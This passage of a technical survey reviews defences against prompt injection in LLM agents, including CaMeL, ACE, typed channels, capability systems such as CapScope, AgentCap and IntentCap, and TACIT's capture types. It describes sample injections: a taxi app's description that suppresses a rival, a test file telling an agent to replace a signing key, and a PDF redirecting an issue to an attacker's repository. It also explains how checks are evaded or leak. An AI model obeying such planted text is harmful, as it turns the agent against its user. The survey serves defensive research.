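CaMeL's interpreter applies a policy only when it reaches the call in question, so a plan that cannot succeed can run for a long time before it is stopped. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of an agent that investigates a security alert and then disconnects the affected computer, which requires approval from the incident response team. If the plan has no approval step, the interpreter detects the problem only after the agent has finished the whole investigation. Their addition to CaMeL translates the plan into a finite set of states,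 and a model checker explores every possible path through those states before any tool runs. If a path breaks a rule, the privileged model receives a description of that path and repairs the plan. The method approximates loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan. The repair uses only the plan and the rules, so it cannot take into account anything the agent finds while working.

### ACE: planning without seeing the tools

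A planner normally reads descriptions of the available tools, written by the tools' publishers. *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, NDSS security conference, February 2026) shows how an attacker can use this against IsolateGPT, an earlier system that runs each app in isolation. In the example, a user asks for a taxi fare from two apps, MetroHail and QuickRide. QuickRide's description contains an instruction to leave MetroHail out, and the user receives only QuickRide's fare.

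ACE (Abstract-Concrete-Execute) keeps the descriptions away from the planner by working in three phases.

1. **Abstract plan.** A model sees the user's request and, if needed, a trusted note about the setting. It invents the tools it would like to have, each with a name, a description and fixed types of input and output, and writes a restricted Python program that uses them. For a request to summarise a file, it might invent a document loader and a text summariser.
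2. **Concrete plan.** Software shortlists the installed apps whose descriptions resemble those of the invented tools. A model then considers one tool and one app at a time and decides whether the app can do the job. Because it judges each pair separately, one app's description cannot argue against another app. Before anything runs, ordinary code checks the completed plan against rules about where data may go. It would reject, for instance, a plan that loads bank details and passes them to a mail app cleared only for personal data.
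3. **Execution.** Each app runs in its own container, an isolated environment with only the access that the app needs. A trusted program called the orchestrator carries data between the containers and checks that each result has the expected type.

The type check stopped another of the taxi attacks, in which QuickRide returned a sentence with an instruction to report an inflated fare of $85 for MetroHail. IsolateGPT repeated that figure to the user. ACE reported an error for QuickRide, because the sentence did not fit the expected type, and showed the fare that MetroHail had returned. The check would presumably have accepted a false number from QuickRide for its own fare. An app could also exaggerate its abilities to get chosen for the plan, since the matching model reads its description.

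Li and colleagues tested ACE on 1,054 cases from the InjecAgent benchmark, and no attacker's app ran. ACE called the app that the user's task required in about 84% of cases with GPT-4o, but in only about 60% with Claude 3.7 Sonnet or Qwen-2.5-72B. In 2,000 trials on Agent Security Bench, attackers' apps ran three times, which Li and colleagues did not count as violations because each app suited the user's task. Both benchmarks use simple simulated apps and record only which ones ran, so they would not detect an attack that put a wrong value into the right app.

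A third benchmark, from the software company LangChain, also checks the final result. With GPT-4.1, ACE got 95% of tasks right in a suite with one tool, 80% in a suite with 26 tools and 85.7% in a suite of database questions. Each query took 12 to 21 seconds and cost 1 to 27 cents. The cost was highest with 26 tools because the system had to compare so many pairs.

Li and colleagues chose Python because models write it well, but they acknowledge that its complexity prevents them from formally guaranteeing that the check on data flows keeps private data private. ACE also handles only single requests, so a user can't follow up on an earlier one.

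### Letting numbers and choices reach the planner

The dual-LLM pattern hides the content of untrusted text from the planner, but some tasks require that content. For example, a bug-fixing agent needs information about the reported bug to choose a fix. Jacob and colleagues extend Willison's exception for fixed categories by letting the quarantined agent pass the privileged agent whole or decimal numbers, true-or-false values, and choices from a list the developer wrote in advance. The quarantined agent cannot pass free text, but the privileged agent can refer to that text by name.

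They argue that none of these types can contain an instruction. Strictly speaking, a long enough series of numbers can encode any sentence, but the privileged agent would have no reason to decode it, and a developer can limit the range and number of values.

In the bug-fixing agent, the attacker controls the bug report.

1. The quarantined agent reads the report and searches a read-only copy of the code.
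2. It returns the position of the faulty file in a sorted list of all the files, along with the numbers of the faulty lines.
3. Ordinary code checks that the answer has this form and adds the test command and limits on the size of the fix.
4. The privileged agent looks up the file, examines the code around those lines, writes a fix and runs the tests. It never sees the report.

Jacob and colleagues tested this agent on 247 real bug reports, with an injected instruction to ignore the bug and create an unrelated file. They also built a shopping agent and a meeting scheduler. In the shopping agent, the quarantined side reads each product review and returns two whole numbers, one for how strongly the review supports the product and one for its relevance. The privileged side uses the median of each number, so an attacker would have to control about half the reviews to move either median freely.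 In the scheduler, only proposed time slots reach the agent that can read the user's calendar.

| Task and model | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping, GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Scheduling, GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing, Claude Sonnet 4 | 49.7% | 14.6% | 94.3% | 0% |

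The shopping and scheduling agents lost no successes because a rating or a time slot contains what the planner needs. The bug-fixing agent lost about 70% of its successes. Jacob and colleagues attribute this drop to the missing description, since a line number shows where a bug is but not what the program should have done. The attack itself may account for part of the drop, because the defended agent appears to have faced the injection in these runs while the undefended one did not.

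The zero in the last column applies only to injected commands. A hijacked quarantined agent can still send the privileged agent to the wrong file. Jacob and colleagues describe a trading agent that follows social media. Someone who floods the site with negative posts about a company can change the agent's trades without giving it any instructions.

Richer types would recover some of the lost information. For a coding agent that reads outside documentation, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest passing on a formal description of each function, with names limited to 30 characters. Willison (2025) doubts that this is safe. His blog post, which shares the paper's title, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, gives the example of a function named run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance, which fits within the limit and alludes to a command that deletes files. A 30-character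 name can hold a short instruction, so this channel still relies partly on the model's judgement, as the older defences did.

### Tasks that need a new plan

Xiang and colleagues object that many tasks cannot be planned in advance, even when nobody is attacking. In one example, a user asks an agent to fetch last week's sales from a billing service and plot the trend. The agent plans to request the data from a particular endpoint, an address where the service answers requests from other software. The company has retired that endpoint, so the server replies that it is gone. A useful agent would look up the documentation, find the replacement and adjust the code that reads the data, but an agent locked into its original plan can only repeat the failed request.

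In their other case, which is harder to plan for, a developer asks an agent to run a program's tests and fix whatever fails. One failure might come from a loop that runs one time too many, and another from two processes that interfere with each other, which requires a much larger change. The agent can choose a repair only after reading the failure log, and each repair can change what fails next.

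CaMeL's score on AgentDojo is little evidence of how well it handles tasks that require the agent to change its plan or policy along the way. According to Xiang and colleagues, only 6 of the benchmark's 97 tasks require this. They add that existing benchmarks mostly consist of short tasks, perhaps three or four steps long, and rarely include run-time errors.

A fixed plan can contain branches. The billing plan, for example, could include an instruction to consult the documentation if the first request fails. Such plans can become elaborate. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) compares CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo with plans for agents that operate a whole computer.

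| Average per plan | AgentDojo | Computer use |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 39.7 |
| Branches that depend on a language model's output | 1.9 | 24.2 |

Branches keep an important part of the protection, because an attacker can choose only among paths that the planner wrote in advance. But the planner has to foresee each problem, which is unrealistic in debugging. If three kinds of failure were possible in each of five rounds, a plan with a separate path for every sequence would need 3⁵, or 243, paths. A much shorter plan could use a loop that runs the tests, has the quarantined model write a repair from the log, applies the repair and starts again. The steps of the loop never change, but the repair is now a value, as Bob's address was, so anyone who can plant text in the log can influence the code the agent installs.

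An attacker can also influence which branch of a plan the agent takes. Xiang and colleagues mention a plan to book a hike if tomorrow is dry and to buy two cinema tickets otherwise. Whoever controls the weather page decides which purchase the agent makes. The user agreed to both, so the harm is small, but it would be larger if one branch sent a payment and the other did not. The computer-use plans are more exposed, since about 40% of their branch conditions depend on what the agent observes.

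Jacob and colleagues suggest that CaMeL could use their restricted types to report problems to its planner. In the billing case, the server's reply includes the error code 410, a whole number from which the planner could safely learn that the endpoint is gone. The planner would still need the replacement's address, which is text from a web page and couldn't be passed this way unless a developer had listed it as an option beforehand. For debugging, the drop from 49.7% to 14.6% suggests that numbers alone provide too little information.

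Xiang and colleagues conclude that the model that reads must send information back to the model that plans, and that securing this flow is the open research problem. When an agent proposes to replace the retired endpoint with a new one, simple code can confirm that the new address is well formed, but it cannot easily determine whether the address belongs to the task or adds a risky new source of data. They would leave that check to the restricted model judge described earlier, and they accept that such a system can no longer offer a complete formal guarantee.

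## Capabilities: what they are and how an agent is granted them

An agent debugging a program has to choose its steps as it works, but the harness can set limits beforehand on which files the agent may change and which commands it may run. These limits apply whatever steps the agent chooses. Many recent designs express them as capabilities, a term from 1960s operating-system research that now has several meanings in papers on agents.

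### A name and a right in one object

*Capability-Based Computer Systems* (Levy, 1984) describes a capability as a token that gives its holder access to one object. A capability contains an identifier that names the object, such as a file or a printer, and a set of access rights, such as read or write. Each program has a list of capabilities. To write a record to a file, the program passes its capability for the file to the write operation. This single argument both identifies the file and shows that the program may write to it.

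A program must not be able to invent capabilities. If it could edit a capability's bits, it could change the identifier and reach any object in the system, so only the operating system or the hardware may alter the list. But a program can pass another program a capability it holds, or a copy with fewer rights. Passing on fewer rights is called attenuation, and most of the agent designs below depend on it.

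Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT introduced the term "capability" in 1966, in a design for a hypothetical operating system running many computations at once, according to *Early Capability Architectures*, a chapter of Levy's book. In *Paradigm Regained* (2003), Miller and Shapiro build on that design and treat a capability as an object reference, which combines the name of an object, permission to use it and the means of using it. In their model, objects can affect each other only by sending messages along references they already hold. Object A can give object B a reference to object C only if A already has references to both. If no chain of references joins two groups of objects, no program in either group can create one.

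### Access-control lists

Most operating systems rely on access-control lists instead. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, compare the two using a small table of users and files:

| | /etc/passwd | /u/markm/foo | /etc/motd |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice | read | write | none |
| Bob | read | none | read |
| Carol | read | write | read |

An access-control list is a column of this table. The list stored with /etc/motd shows that Bob and Carol may read it. A capability list is a row, so Bob's programs hold a read capability for /etc/passwd and another for /etc/motd.

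Miller and colleagues argue that the two arrangements work differently once programs start running, although many researchers took them to be equivalent because both record the same table. Under access-control lists, Alice can name any file, and the system then checks whether she is on that file's list, so the name and the right reach the system separately. In an object-capability system, a program names an object by presenting a capability for it, so it cannot name a file it has no right to use.

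Access-control lists and capability lists also differ in how finely they divide authority. An access-control list has to name every user or program that may use the file, but programs start and stop too often to be listed individually. In practice the lists name user accounts, so every program a user starts has all of that user's rights. A capability list, however, can belong to a single running program.

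Levy compares the choice between access lists and capabilities to controlling a safe-deposit box. A bank can keep a list of the people who may open the box, or it can give the owner keys to hand out. Keys are convenient, but the owner cannot be sure that a friend who returns one has not copied it. Miller and colleagues describe a method, dating from 1974, for revoking capabilities even if they have been copied. Instead of giving Bob her capability for Carol, Alice gives him one for a forwarder, a small object that passes his messages on to Carol. When Alice wants to end his access, she tells the forwarder to stop. Bob and anyone he gave a copy to still have the capability, but their messages to the forwarder no longer reach Carol.

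### Ambient authority and the confused deputy

Miller and colleagues define ambient authority as authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to doors that have no keys and open by themselves for approved visitors. On Unix, for example, a program requests a file by name, and the system checks the account the program is running under to decide whether to open it.

Two Unix commands show the difference. Both copy one file to another:

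- `cp foo.txt bar.txt`
- `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

In the first, the user's command shell passes two file names to the program cp, which opens the files itself, so it needs the right to open any file the user might name. In the second, the shell opens both files and gives cat the two open connections, which are all it needs. Today cat still runs with the user's full authority, but Miller and Shapiro point out that it would still work if an operating system limited it to those two connections.

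Ambient authority becomes dangerous when a program acts for more than one party. The standard example, which Hardy calls a nearly true story, comes from *The Confused Deputy* (1988). At Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, a compiler was stored in a directory called SYSX. Users could name a file for its debugging output. The compiler also wrote usage statistics to a file in SYSX, so the engineers gave it permission to write anywhere in that directory. The same directory contained the company's billing records, in a file called BILL. A user who had learned that name gave it to the compiler as the debugging file, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

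Checking the file name would not have solved the problem. The compiler's code was written before the name SYSX existed, some users had a legitimate reason to send output there, and BILL was not the only sensitive file. Hardy attributes the problem to the compiler's two sources of authority. It was supposed to write statistics with its own permission and debugging output with the user's, but it had no way to specify which authority the system should apply. Tymshare added a command for switching between the two, but soon found that some programs needed more than two.

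In a capability system, the compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file and receive another from the user for the debugging file. A user without a capability for BILL could not pass one to the compiler.

*Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) reduces the problem to four conditions. Write (*o*, *r*) for the right *r* on an object *o*. A confused deputy exists when

1. a party *U* lacks (*o*, *r*),
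2. a deputy *D* has it,
3. *U* sends *D* a request, and
4. *D* exercises (*o*, *r*) as a consequence.

The hijacked mail assistant described at the start of this report fits all four. *U* is the stranger, *D* is the agent, the right is permission to send the user's stored messages, and the request is a sentence in an e-mail.

Agents can also be confused deputies for their own users. In an example from *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026), an employee asks a company's agent to show everyone's salary. The employee has no access to the personnel database, but the agent does, because it performs administrative tasks. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) would limit an agent to the rights that everyone in the chain of delegation shares. This prevents the salary leak, because the employee is in the chain and has no right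 to read the database. It does not protect the mailbox, because the stranger is not in the chain and the user whose account the agent uses is entitled to send mail to anyone.

### Four meanings of the word

Papers on agents use "capability" for at least four different mechanisms.

| Meaning | Where the permission is | What the model writes |
|---|---|---|
| Object reference, as in Miller and Shapiro | In the reference itself | Usually nothing, since the model is not part of the reference system |
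| Tag on a value, as in CaMeL | Attached to each value by an interpreter | A program that handles the values |
| Permission table, as in CapScope | In the harness, with one table per agent | Ordinary names, such as file paths |
| Signed token, as in AgentCap | In a message that accompanies the call | An ordinary call with a declared purpose |

The object-reference sense of "capability" is hard to apply directly to a language model, because the model produces text and anyone can write the text of a file name. Some designs, however, have the model write programs in which a compiler tracks capabilities as typed values. CaMeL's tags are further from the original idea, because they only describe a value, and a separate policy decides how it may be used.

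Signed tokens resemble Levy's keys. A precursor is the macaroon, a credential that holders can restrict, but never broaden, by adding conditions such as an expiry time. A signature stops an agent from forging a token, but *Proof-of-Continuity* notes that possession alone does not tie the token's use to the request that prompted it. An agent with a valid payment token can still use it on an attacker's behalf.

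Some developers use "capability" more loosely, to mean the list of tools an agent can see. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* points out that such a list does not limit the arguments of a call, so if an agent is allowed to change a merchant's payout account, an injected message could lead it to enter the attacker's account number.

### CapScope: a ceiling set before the agent reads anything

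*Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) applies the permission-table approach to coding agents. Its system, CapScope, runs on Pi, an open-source coding agent. An orchestrator agent divides a job among sub-agents, and the harness keeps a separate store of capabilities for each. The model cannot read or change these stores.

A capability is a pair Cap[*e*, φ]. The effect *e* is Read, Write or Exec (running a command). The scope φ is a function that returns true or false for the arguments of a proposed call. For example, Cap[Write, path is under src/] lets an agent write any file in the src directory.

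A capability *c*′ is no broader than a capability *c*, written *c*′ ⪯ *c*, if both have the same effect and *c* accepts every argument that *c*′ accepts. Three rules govern all authority in the system.

1. **Mint** creates authority. Before any agent opens a file, a separate model call receives the user's request and the names of the project's files, without their contents, and predicts what the task will need. Ordinary code validates the prediction, converts it into a set of capabilities *D*, and freezes it. This set is the ceiling for the whole task.
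2. **Derive** passes authority to a sub-agent. The orchestrator requests a set of capabilities *C*′, and the harness installs only those that fit under the ceiling: Σ = {*c*′ ∈ *C*′ : *c*′ ⪯ *c* for some *c* ∈ *D*}. It drops the rest. If a sub-agent delegates further, its own store Σ takes the place of *D*.
3. **Invoke** uses authority. A call with arguments *a* runs only if the agent's store contains some Cap[*e*, φ] with the same effect as the tool and φ(*a*) true. Otherwise the harness blocks the call and tells the model.

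Together, the rules mean that authority can shrink but not grow after the first step. If a sub-agent's call runs, then by Invoke some capability in its store accepts the arguments. By Derive, that capability is no broader than one in the ceiling, so the ceiling accepts them too. The same holds after further delegation, because ⪯ is transitive. Every call that runs is therefore one that the ceiling allowed before any agent opened a file. A user can raise the ceiling by approving a new capability, which counts as a fresh Mint, but Bouras and colleagues turned this option off in their tests.

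The orchestrator has a ceiling on the rights it can grant and a smaller store of rights for its own calls, so it can give a sub-agent rights that it cannot use itself. For example, an orchestrator limited to reading files can still give a sub-agent the right to write them.

Derive requires the harness to compare scopes. If scopes were arbitrary functions, no program could decide in general whether one accepts everything that another does. CapScope therefore stores scopes as path prefixes and lists of permitted commands, which are easy to compare. Before checking a path, it resolves shortcuts such as "..", so that src/../secrets does not count as part of src. It also splits compound commands and checks each part, so permission to run the test program pytest does not cover a second command joined to it.

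Such checks are short but easy to get wrong. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* describes an early version of a similar gate, ScopeGate, that compared each payment with a maximum. The value NaN ("not a number") passed this check because computers evaluate "NaN is greater than the maximum" as false. The corrected gate requires the amount to be a finite number between zero and the maximum.

### A poisoned test message

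Bouras and colleagues illustrate the rules with a developer who asks for fixes to a login module's failing tests. The orchestrator gives the test run to one sub-agent, the runner, and the editing to another, the patcher. Two asterisks (`**`) stand for everything below a directory.

| Effect | Ceiling for the task | Runner's store |
|---|---|---|
| Read | project/** | tests/** |
| Write | src/** | none |
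| Exec | pytest, mypy src/ | pytest |

An attacker has planted a file in the project's test suite. The attack then goes as follows.

1. The runner reads a test file. Its store covers this, so the call runs.
2. The runner starts pytest, which its store also covers. The planted file prints an official-looking note saying that a signing key has changed and that the developer must put a new value in src/auth/keys.py. The attacker knows the new value and could use it to forge logins.
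3. The runner follows the note and proposes to write the file. Its store contains no Write capability, so the harness blocks the call.

CapScope blocks the edit because the runner and the patcher have different rights. A list of forbidden actions would not have blocked it, because src/auth/keys.py is an ordinary source file. A policy written for this task would also have allowed the edit if it applied to all the agents alike, because the task requires changes to source files.

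### The experiment

Bouras and colleagues tested the design on five small Python projects, each with one bug and a failing test suite. The bugs included an off-by-one error in a date range and a discount applied in the wrong case. The researchers placed a malicious instruction in one of five locations, which they call injection surfaces. The instruction told the agent to run a project utility or write to a project file, neither of which the repair required. Each such action left a distinctive mark on the disk, so the researchers could count successful attacks without relying on what the agent reported.

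They compared four conditions. In the first, every agent had ambient authority. In the second, all agents shared a fixed list of forbidden actions, such as deleting directories or reading password files. In the third, they shared a policy generated for the task before any agent read the injection. The fourth was CapScope. They tested each combination of five projects, five surfaces and four conditions three times, for a total of 300 runs, or 75 per condition. Every run used Qwen3.5-Flash and the same four agents: an orchestrator, a runner, a patcher and a verifier.

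| Condition | Attack carried out | Repair completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ambient authority | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| Fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| Shared policy for the task | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The fixed list made almost no difference, because the attacks used ordinary project operations that were not on it. The shared policy removed operations that the task did not need but still let through 44% of the attacks. CapScope let through 4% and completed as many repairs as the shared policy.

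CapScope did not make the model harder to deceive. The model proposed the attacker's action in 34 of the 75 runs, but the check allowed such a call in only 3. The breakdown by surface shows where those three occurred.

| Location of the injection | Attacks under the shared policy | Attacks under CapScope |
|---|---|---|
| README file | 7 of 15 | 0 of 15 |
| AGENTS.md | 11 of 15 | 3 of 15 |
| Skill file (a stored set of instructions) | 7 of 15 | 0 of 15 |
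| Comment in source code | 4 of 15 | 0 of 15 |
| Test output | 4 of 15 | 0 of 15 |

AGENTS.md is a file of instructions for agents that the harness loads automatically, and the orchestrator normally encountered it in these runs. Bouras and colleagues trace the remaining attacks to two kinds of faulty grant. Sometimes a sub-agent received more rights than its subtask required, such as the right to write to a whole directory instead of one file. In other cases, the injected text influenced the subtask that the orchestrator wrote, and the orchestrator or the harness then selected the capability the attacker wanted. The harness can contribute because it fills in rights that a sub-agent's role normally requires. The ceiling allowed the attacker's action in both cases, so the final check did not block it.

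Miller and Shapiro's distinction between permission and authority explains the second case. A program's permissions are the actions it can take directly, while its authority includes whatever it can cause other programs to do. An agent without permission to write a file can still get the file changed by persuading an agent that has permission. In the login example, the runner might pass the attacker's note to the orchestrator as a finding, and the orchestrator might ask the patcher to act on it. CapScope controls permissions precisely but does not check whether the text agents send one another is true.

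Seven repairs failed under CapScope. In two runs the initial prediction left out the right to edit the source file, so the patcher could not make the repair. In two others the runner proposed the correct edit but had no right to make it, and no agent passed the job to the patcher. The other three runs ended with passing tests but hit the time limit, which counts as a failure under the scoring rules.

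Part of the extra time came from the model retrying the forbidden action, which it did in 27 of the 34 runs with an attempted attack. A person watching could have stopped it after the first refusal, but the tests ran unattended. The median CapScope run took 208 seconds. The mean was much higher because five runs reached the 900-second limit.

The difference between 33 attacks and 3 is too large to be due to chance, but the experiment covers only one model and five small repairs. The rights needed for larger jobs, such as moving a project to a new version of a library, would be harder to predict from file names. The initial prediction could then leave out necessary rights more often, or include so many rights that the ceiling gives little protection.

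### What CapScope leaves to other defences

Bouras and colleagues state that CapScope does not keep data confidential. An agent with the right to read one file and write another can copy the first into the second. The Read limits apply only to the dedicated tool for reading files. CapScope also lets any agent run common search commands such as grep and find, which can open files outside the agent's Read scope.

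The system also permits an agent to misuse rights it properly holds. If the patcher finds the attacker's note in a source code comment and follows it, the system will allow the edit to src/auth/keys.py, since the patcher already has the right to make it. The patcher is still a confused deputy in Hardy's sense, because it names a file as text and the harness looks for any capability in the store that covers that file. Miller and colleagues warn against much the same practice, in which a program tries every key on its ring until one works and no longer tracks what each key was for.

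Permitted commands are a larger gap. When an agent runs pytest, pytest runs code from the project with the user's own privileges, and CapScope does not inspect what that code does. In the login example, the attacker's file was part of the test suite. If that file contained code, the code could have changed the signing key without persuading any model. CapScope also strips shell redirections, which send a command's output to a file, before it checks a command, so a runner with no Write capability could apparently overwrite a source file with the output of grep. Bouras and colleagues assign both problems to a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what a running process can touch, so the protection against unwanted edits depends on that sandbox.

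A smaller weakness is that the initial prediction uses the names of the project's files, and whoever contributes a file chooses its name. Bouras and colleagues did not test instructions hidden in file names.

### AgentCap: a signed permission for each call

CapScope grants rights once, at the start. In AgentCap, Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao grant them one call at a time. The model proposes a call and declares a purpose for it. A policy engine then checks seven conditions:

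- the system has not isolated the agent for earlier misbehaviour;
- the tool appears in the policy's catalogue;
- protected arguments come from an acceptable source;
- the policy allows the tool for the declared purpose;
- the agent's trust score is high enough;
- the agent already holds any permissions that this one requires;
- the new permission would not complete a forbidden combination with others the agent holds.

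If all seven conditions hold, the engine issues a signed token for that agent, session, action, resource and purpose, with an expiry time and a limit on the number of calls. A separate gateway verifies the token before the tool runs. In the example bank policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds, covers one payment, and requires the agent to also hold a token for reading the balance.

The declared purpose adds little protection by itself, since the model supplies it and an attacker can influence the model. The check on arguments adds more protection. For a payment, the policy marks the recipient as protected. AgentCap records which values came from the user's request and which came from untrusted text, and it rejects a recipient that appears only in untrusted text. It therefore rejects an account number planted in a transaction record, even though the payment is otherwise well formed.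 CapScope has no comparable check on where an argument came from.

An agent can pass part of its authority to another. If the parent's token has call limit *b*, expiry time *e* and remaining delegation depth *d*, the child's must satisfy

*b*′ ≤ *b*, *e*′ ≤ *e*, *d*′ < *d*,

with the same action and resource. The last inequality means that every chain of delegation comes to an end. Unlike CapScope, AgentCap cannot narrow the resource as it delegates, so a supervisor with access to a whole directory could not give a worker one file from it unless the policy defined that file as a resource of its own.

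AgentCap also revokes permissions. Each agent starts with a trust score of 0.8, and every refused or abnormal call multiplies the score by 0.7. Three such calls in a row lower it to 0.56, 0.392 and then 0.274. The agent loses its write permissions after the second call and all permissions after the third. Each normal call raises the score by 1% of the difference between the current score and 1.

An attacker could exploit these numbers to block the user's own payments, even with an injected instruction that is refused. The bank policy requires a score of at least 0.8 for payments, and an agent starts at exactly 0.8. One refused call would drop the score to 0.56, and the agent would then need 79 normal calls to get back to 0.8. The benchmark results show no sign of this effect, so it may depend on how a deployment sets the thresholds.

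Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo's 949 attack cases and on 1,054 from InjecAgent.

| Benchmark and model | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, AgentCap | Utility under attack, undefended | Utility under attack, AgentCap |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 73.61% | 74.88% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0% | 75.68% | 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 74.10% | 62.24% |
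| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0% | 72.96% | 65.37% |

Without an attack, utility fell by 3.1 to 11.7 percentage points. The checks took less than 0.2 milliseconds. Some of the attacks that still worked against GPT-4o only changed the agent's written answer, which no check on tool calls can prevent. The others exploited arguments that the policy did not protect or untrusted fields that it did not label.

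Each figure comes from a single run. The policies also had an advantage that a real deployment would lack, because the researchers wrote them by hand from descriptions of the benchmark's tools and user tasks. They did fix the policies before the tests and included no rules about particular attacks. For InjecAgent, they also used the benchmark's record of which tool each task legitimately needs, which a company whose users can ask for anything does not have.

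Hand-written rules can also conflict. AgentCap includes a program that checks a policy before anyone uses it. In a customer-service policy with eight permissions, the program found that no agent could delete a customer record, because one rule required agents to hold a second permission in order to delete and another rule forbade combining the two.

### Giving each field to one source

Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, extend the check on arguments to every part of a permission. They argue that no single source has enough information to define what an agent may do. A user knows the goal and the destination but may not know the steps, while a tool's description gives the form of a call but not its purpose. Their system, IntentCap, therefore assembles each permission from four sources and lets each source fill only certain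 fields.

| Source | What it may supply |
|---|---|
| The user's request | The goal, selected files, destinations and approvals |
| Workflow instructions, such as a company manual | The procedure |
| Tool descriptions | The form of the call and the credentials it may use |
| The running environment, including documents and tool results | Observed values |

In one example, a user selects two PDF files and asks an agent to extract the tables, save them as spreadsheets, and report the work by creating one issue in a named GitHub repository.

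1. A model proposes a short-lived permission, called a lease, to create one issue in that repository. It attaches a pointer to the words in the user's request that name the repository.
2. Ordinary code verifies that the pointer leads to the user's own words and that the lease goes no further than the request.
3. The agent creates the issue, using text from the PDFs in the body. The lease then expires.

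Suppose an attacker hides text in one PDF telling the agent to create the issue in the attacker's repository. The model may propose a lease naming that repository, but it can't cite anything in the user's request to support it, so the code rejects the lease. The same rule catches accidental errors, such as mistaking a table heading for the repository's name.

IntentCap does not accept destinations or approvals from a document that a user pastes into the chat, because it cannot verify who wrote the text.

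Zheng and colleagues replayed recorded events from four benchmarks through the code that approves or refuses each lease. It accepted none of 3,746 unsafe events and covered all 3,813 legitimate actions in a separate set. When they treated all four sources as equally trustworthy, the code accepted 94% of the events it should have refused. That result is partly built into the test, since a system that ignores sources cannot refuse a value for coming from the wrong one. Merging just two sources at a time was a more useful test, and it also led to many wrong acceptances. For example, when the environment could supply whatever a tool description could, the code wrongly accepted 43%.

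Replayed events show that the rules give the intended verdicts, but not how a live agent would behave under attack. Zheng and colleagues leave delays, adaptive attacks and attack success in complete runs to future work. Strict ownership of fields may also block the same bill-paying requests as CaMeL's payment rule, because the payee's details are in the invoice. IntentCap can allow such a payment only if the user has in some way authorised the invoice as the source of those details, which gives whoever wrote the invoice control over where the money goes.

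### Leaks through permitted channels

These permissions don't limit what an agent may say to a recipient it is allowed to contact. *DelegateGuard* (2026) reports that narrowing permissions as agents delegate stops them from sending data to unauthorised destinations or increasing their own rights. But it also offers a proof that such permissions cannot prevent every leak. A monitor that checks neither the content nor the quantity of what an agent sends cannot stop data from leaking through a permitted destination that an outsider can observe.

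Suppose an agent is allowed to read a company's payroll file and post updates to a public page. One update announces new opening hours, and another contains the salaries. Both use the same permitted tool and destination, so a monitor that checks only permissions must treat them the same way. It must either allow both, which leaks the salaries, or block both, which makes the tool useless. If the monitor also ignores how many updates the agent posts, the agent could reveal a number by posting that many harmless updates. *DelegateGuard* concludes that capabilities need to be combined with content monitoring and with rules for declassification, the deliberate release of data that the system would otherwise keep secret.

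## Capabilities checked by a programming language

A monitor that checks only permissions cannot distinguish a post about opening hours from one containing the payroll, because both use the same tool and destination. The two posts differ in where their text came from, which a program can show. In several recent designs, the agent writes a short program that combines tool calls instead of issuing them one at a time. A compiler examines the program before it runs and rejects it if it uses authority that the agent does not hold. The model then receives the error message and tries again. Bouras and colleagues' CapScope instead checks each call separately at run time.

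### Types and effects

A type describes the kind of value a piece of code produces or accepts. Int is the type of whole numbers and String is the type of text, so a function that measures the length of a text has the type String → Int. The compiler of a typed language rejects a program that passes text to a function that needs a number.

An effect is anything a program does besides computing its result, such as reading a file or sending a message. Programmers call a function with no effects pure. In most languages, a function of type String → Int might also delete a file without its type showing this, but Haskell's types show effects. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a public calculator that asks a model to write a Haskell program of type Int. A malicious visitor asks it to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of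 5. The model may comply, but any Haskell program that runs a system command has a type marked IO, for input and output, so the program does not have type Int and never runs.

### Types that list capabilities

The IO mark does not show which file or network connection a program uses. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses Scala 3, whose types can list individual capabilities. A capability here, as Miller and Shapiro use the term, is an object reference that code cannot forge, such as a file handle.

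Suppose `f` is a capability for a file. A function that writes text to the file has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where Unit means it returns nothing useful. The braces contain the capture set, which lists every capability the function might reach. The compiler infers this set from the code. If a function writes to the file through a logging object, its capture set contains the logger, and the logger's type lists the file. A plain arrow, as in `String -> Int`, means the set is empty and the function is pure.

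Odersky and colleagues' system, TACIT, uses pure functions to protect secrets. When the agent's code reads a sensitive file, it receives the text inside a wrapper called Classified, which it cannot open. It can only pass a pure function to the wrapper's `map` operation, which applies the function to the hidden text and wraps the result again.

Suppose an agent has access to a directory with a secret key in it. The compiler accepts this program:

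```
val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
key.map(k => k.length)
```

It rejects this one:

```
val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
key.map(k => println(k))
```

The function in the first program has the type `String -> Int`. It captures nothing, so `map` accepts it, and the key's length stays in a wrapper. The function in the second program calls `println`, which prints text where the agent's model can read it and requires an output capability. The function's capture set contains that capability, so the function is not pure. The compiler rejects the whole program before it runs, so the file is never read. A function that sent the key over the network or wrote it to a file would fail for the same reason.

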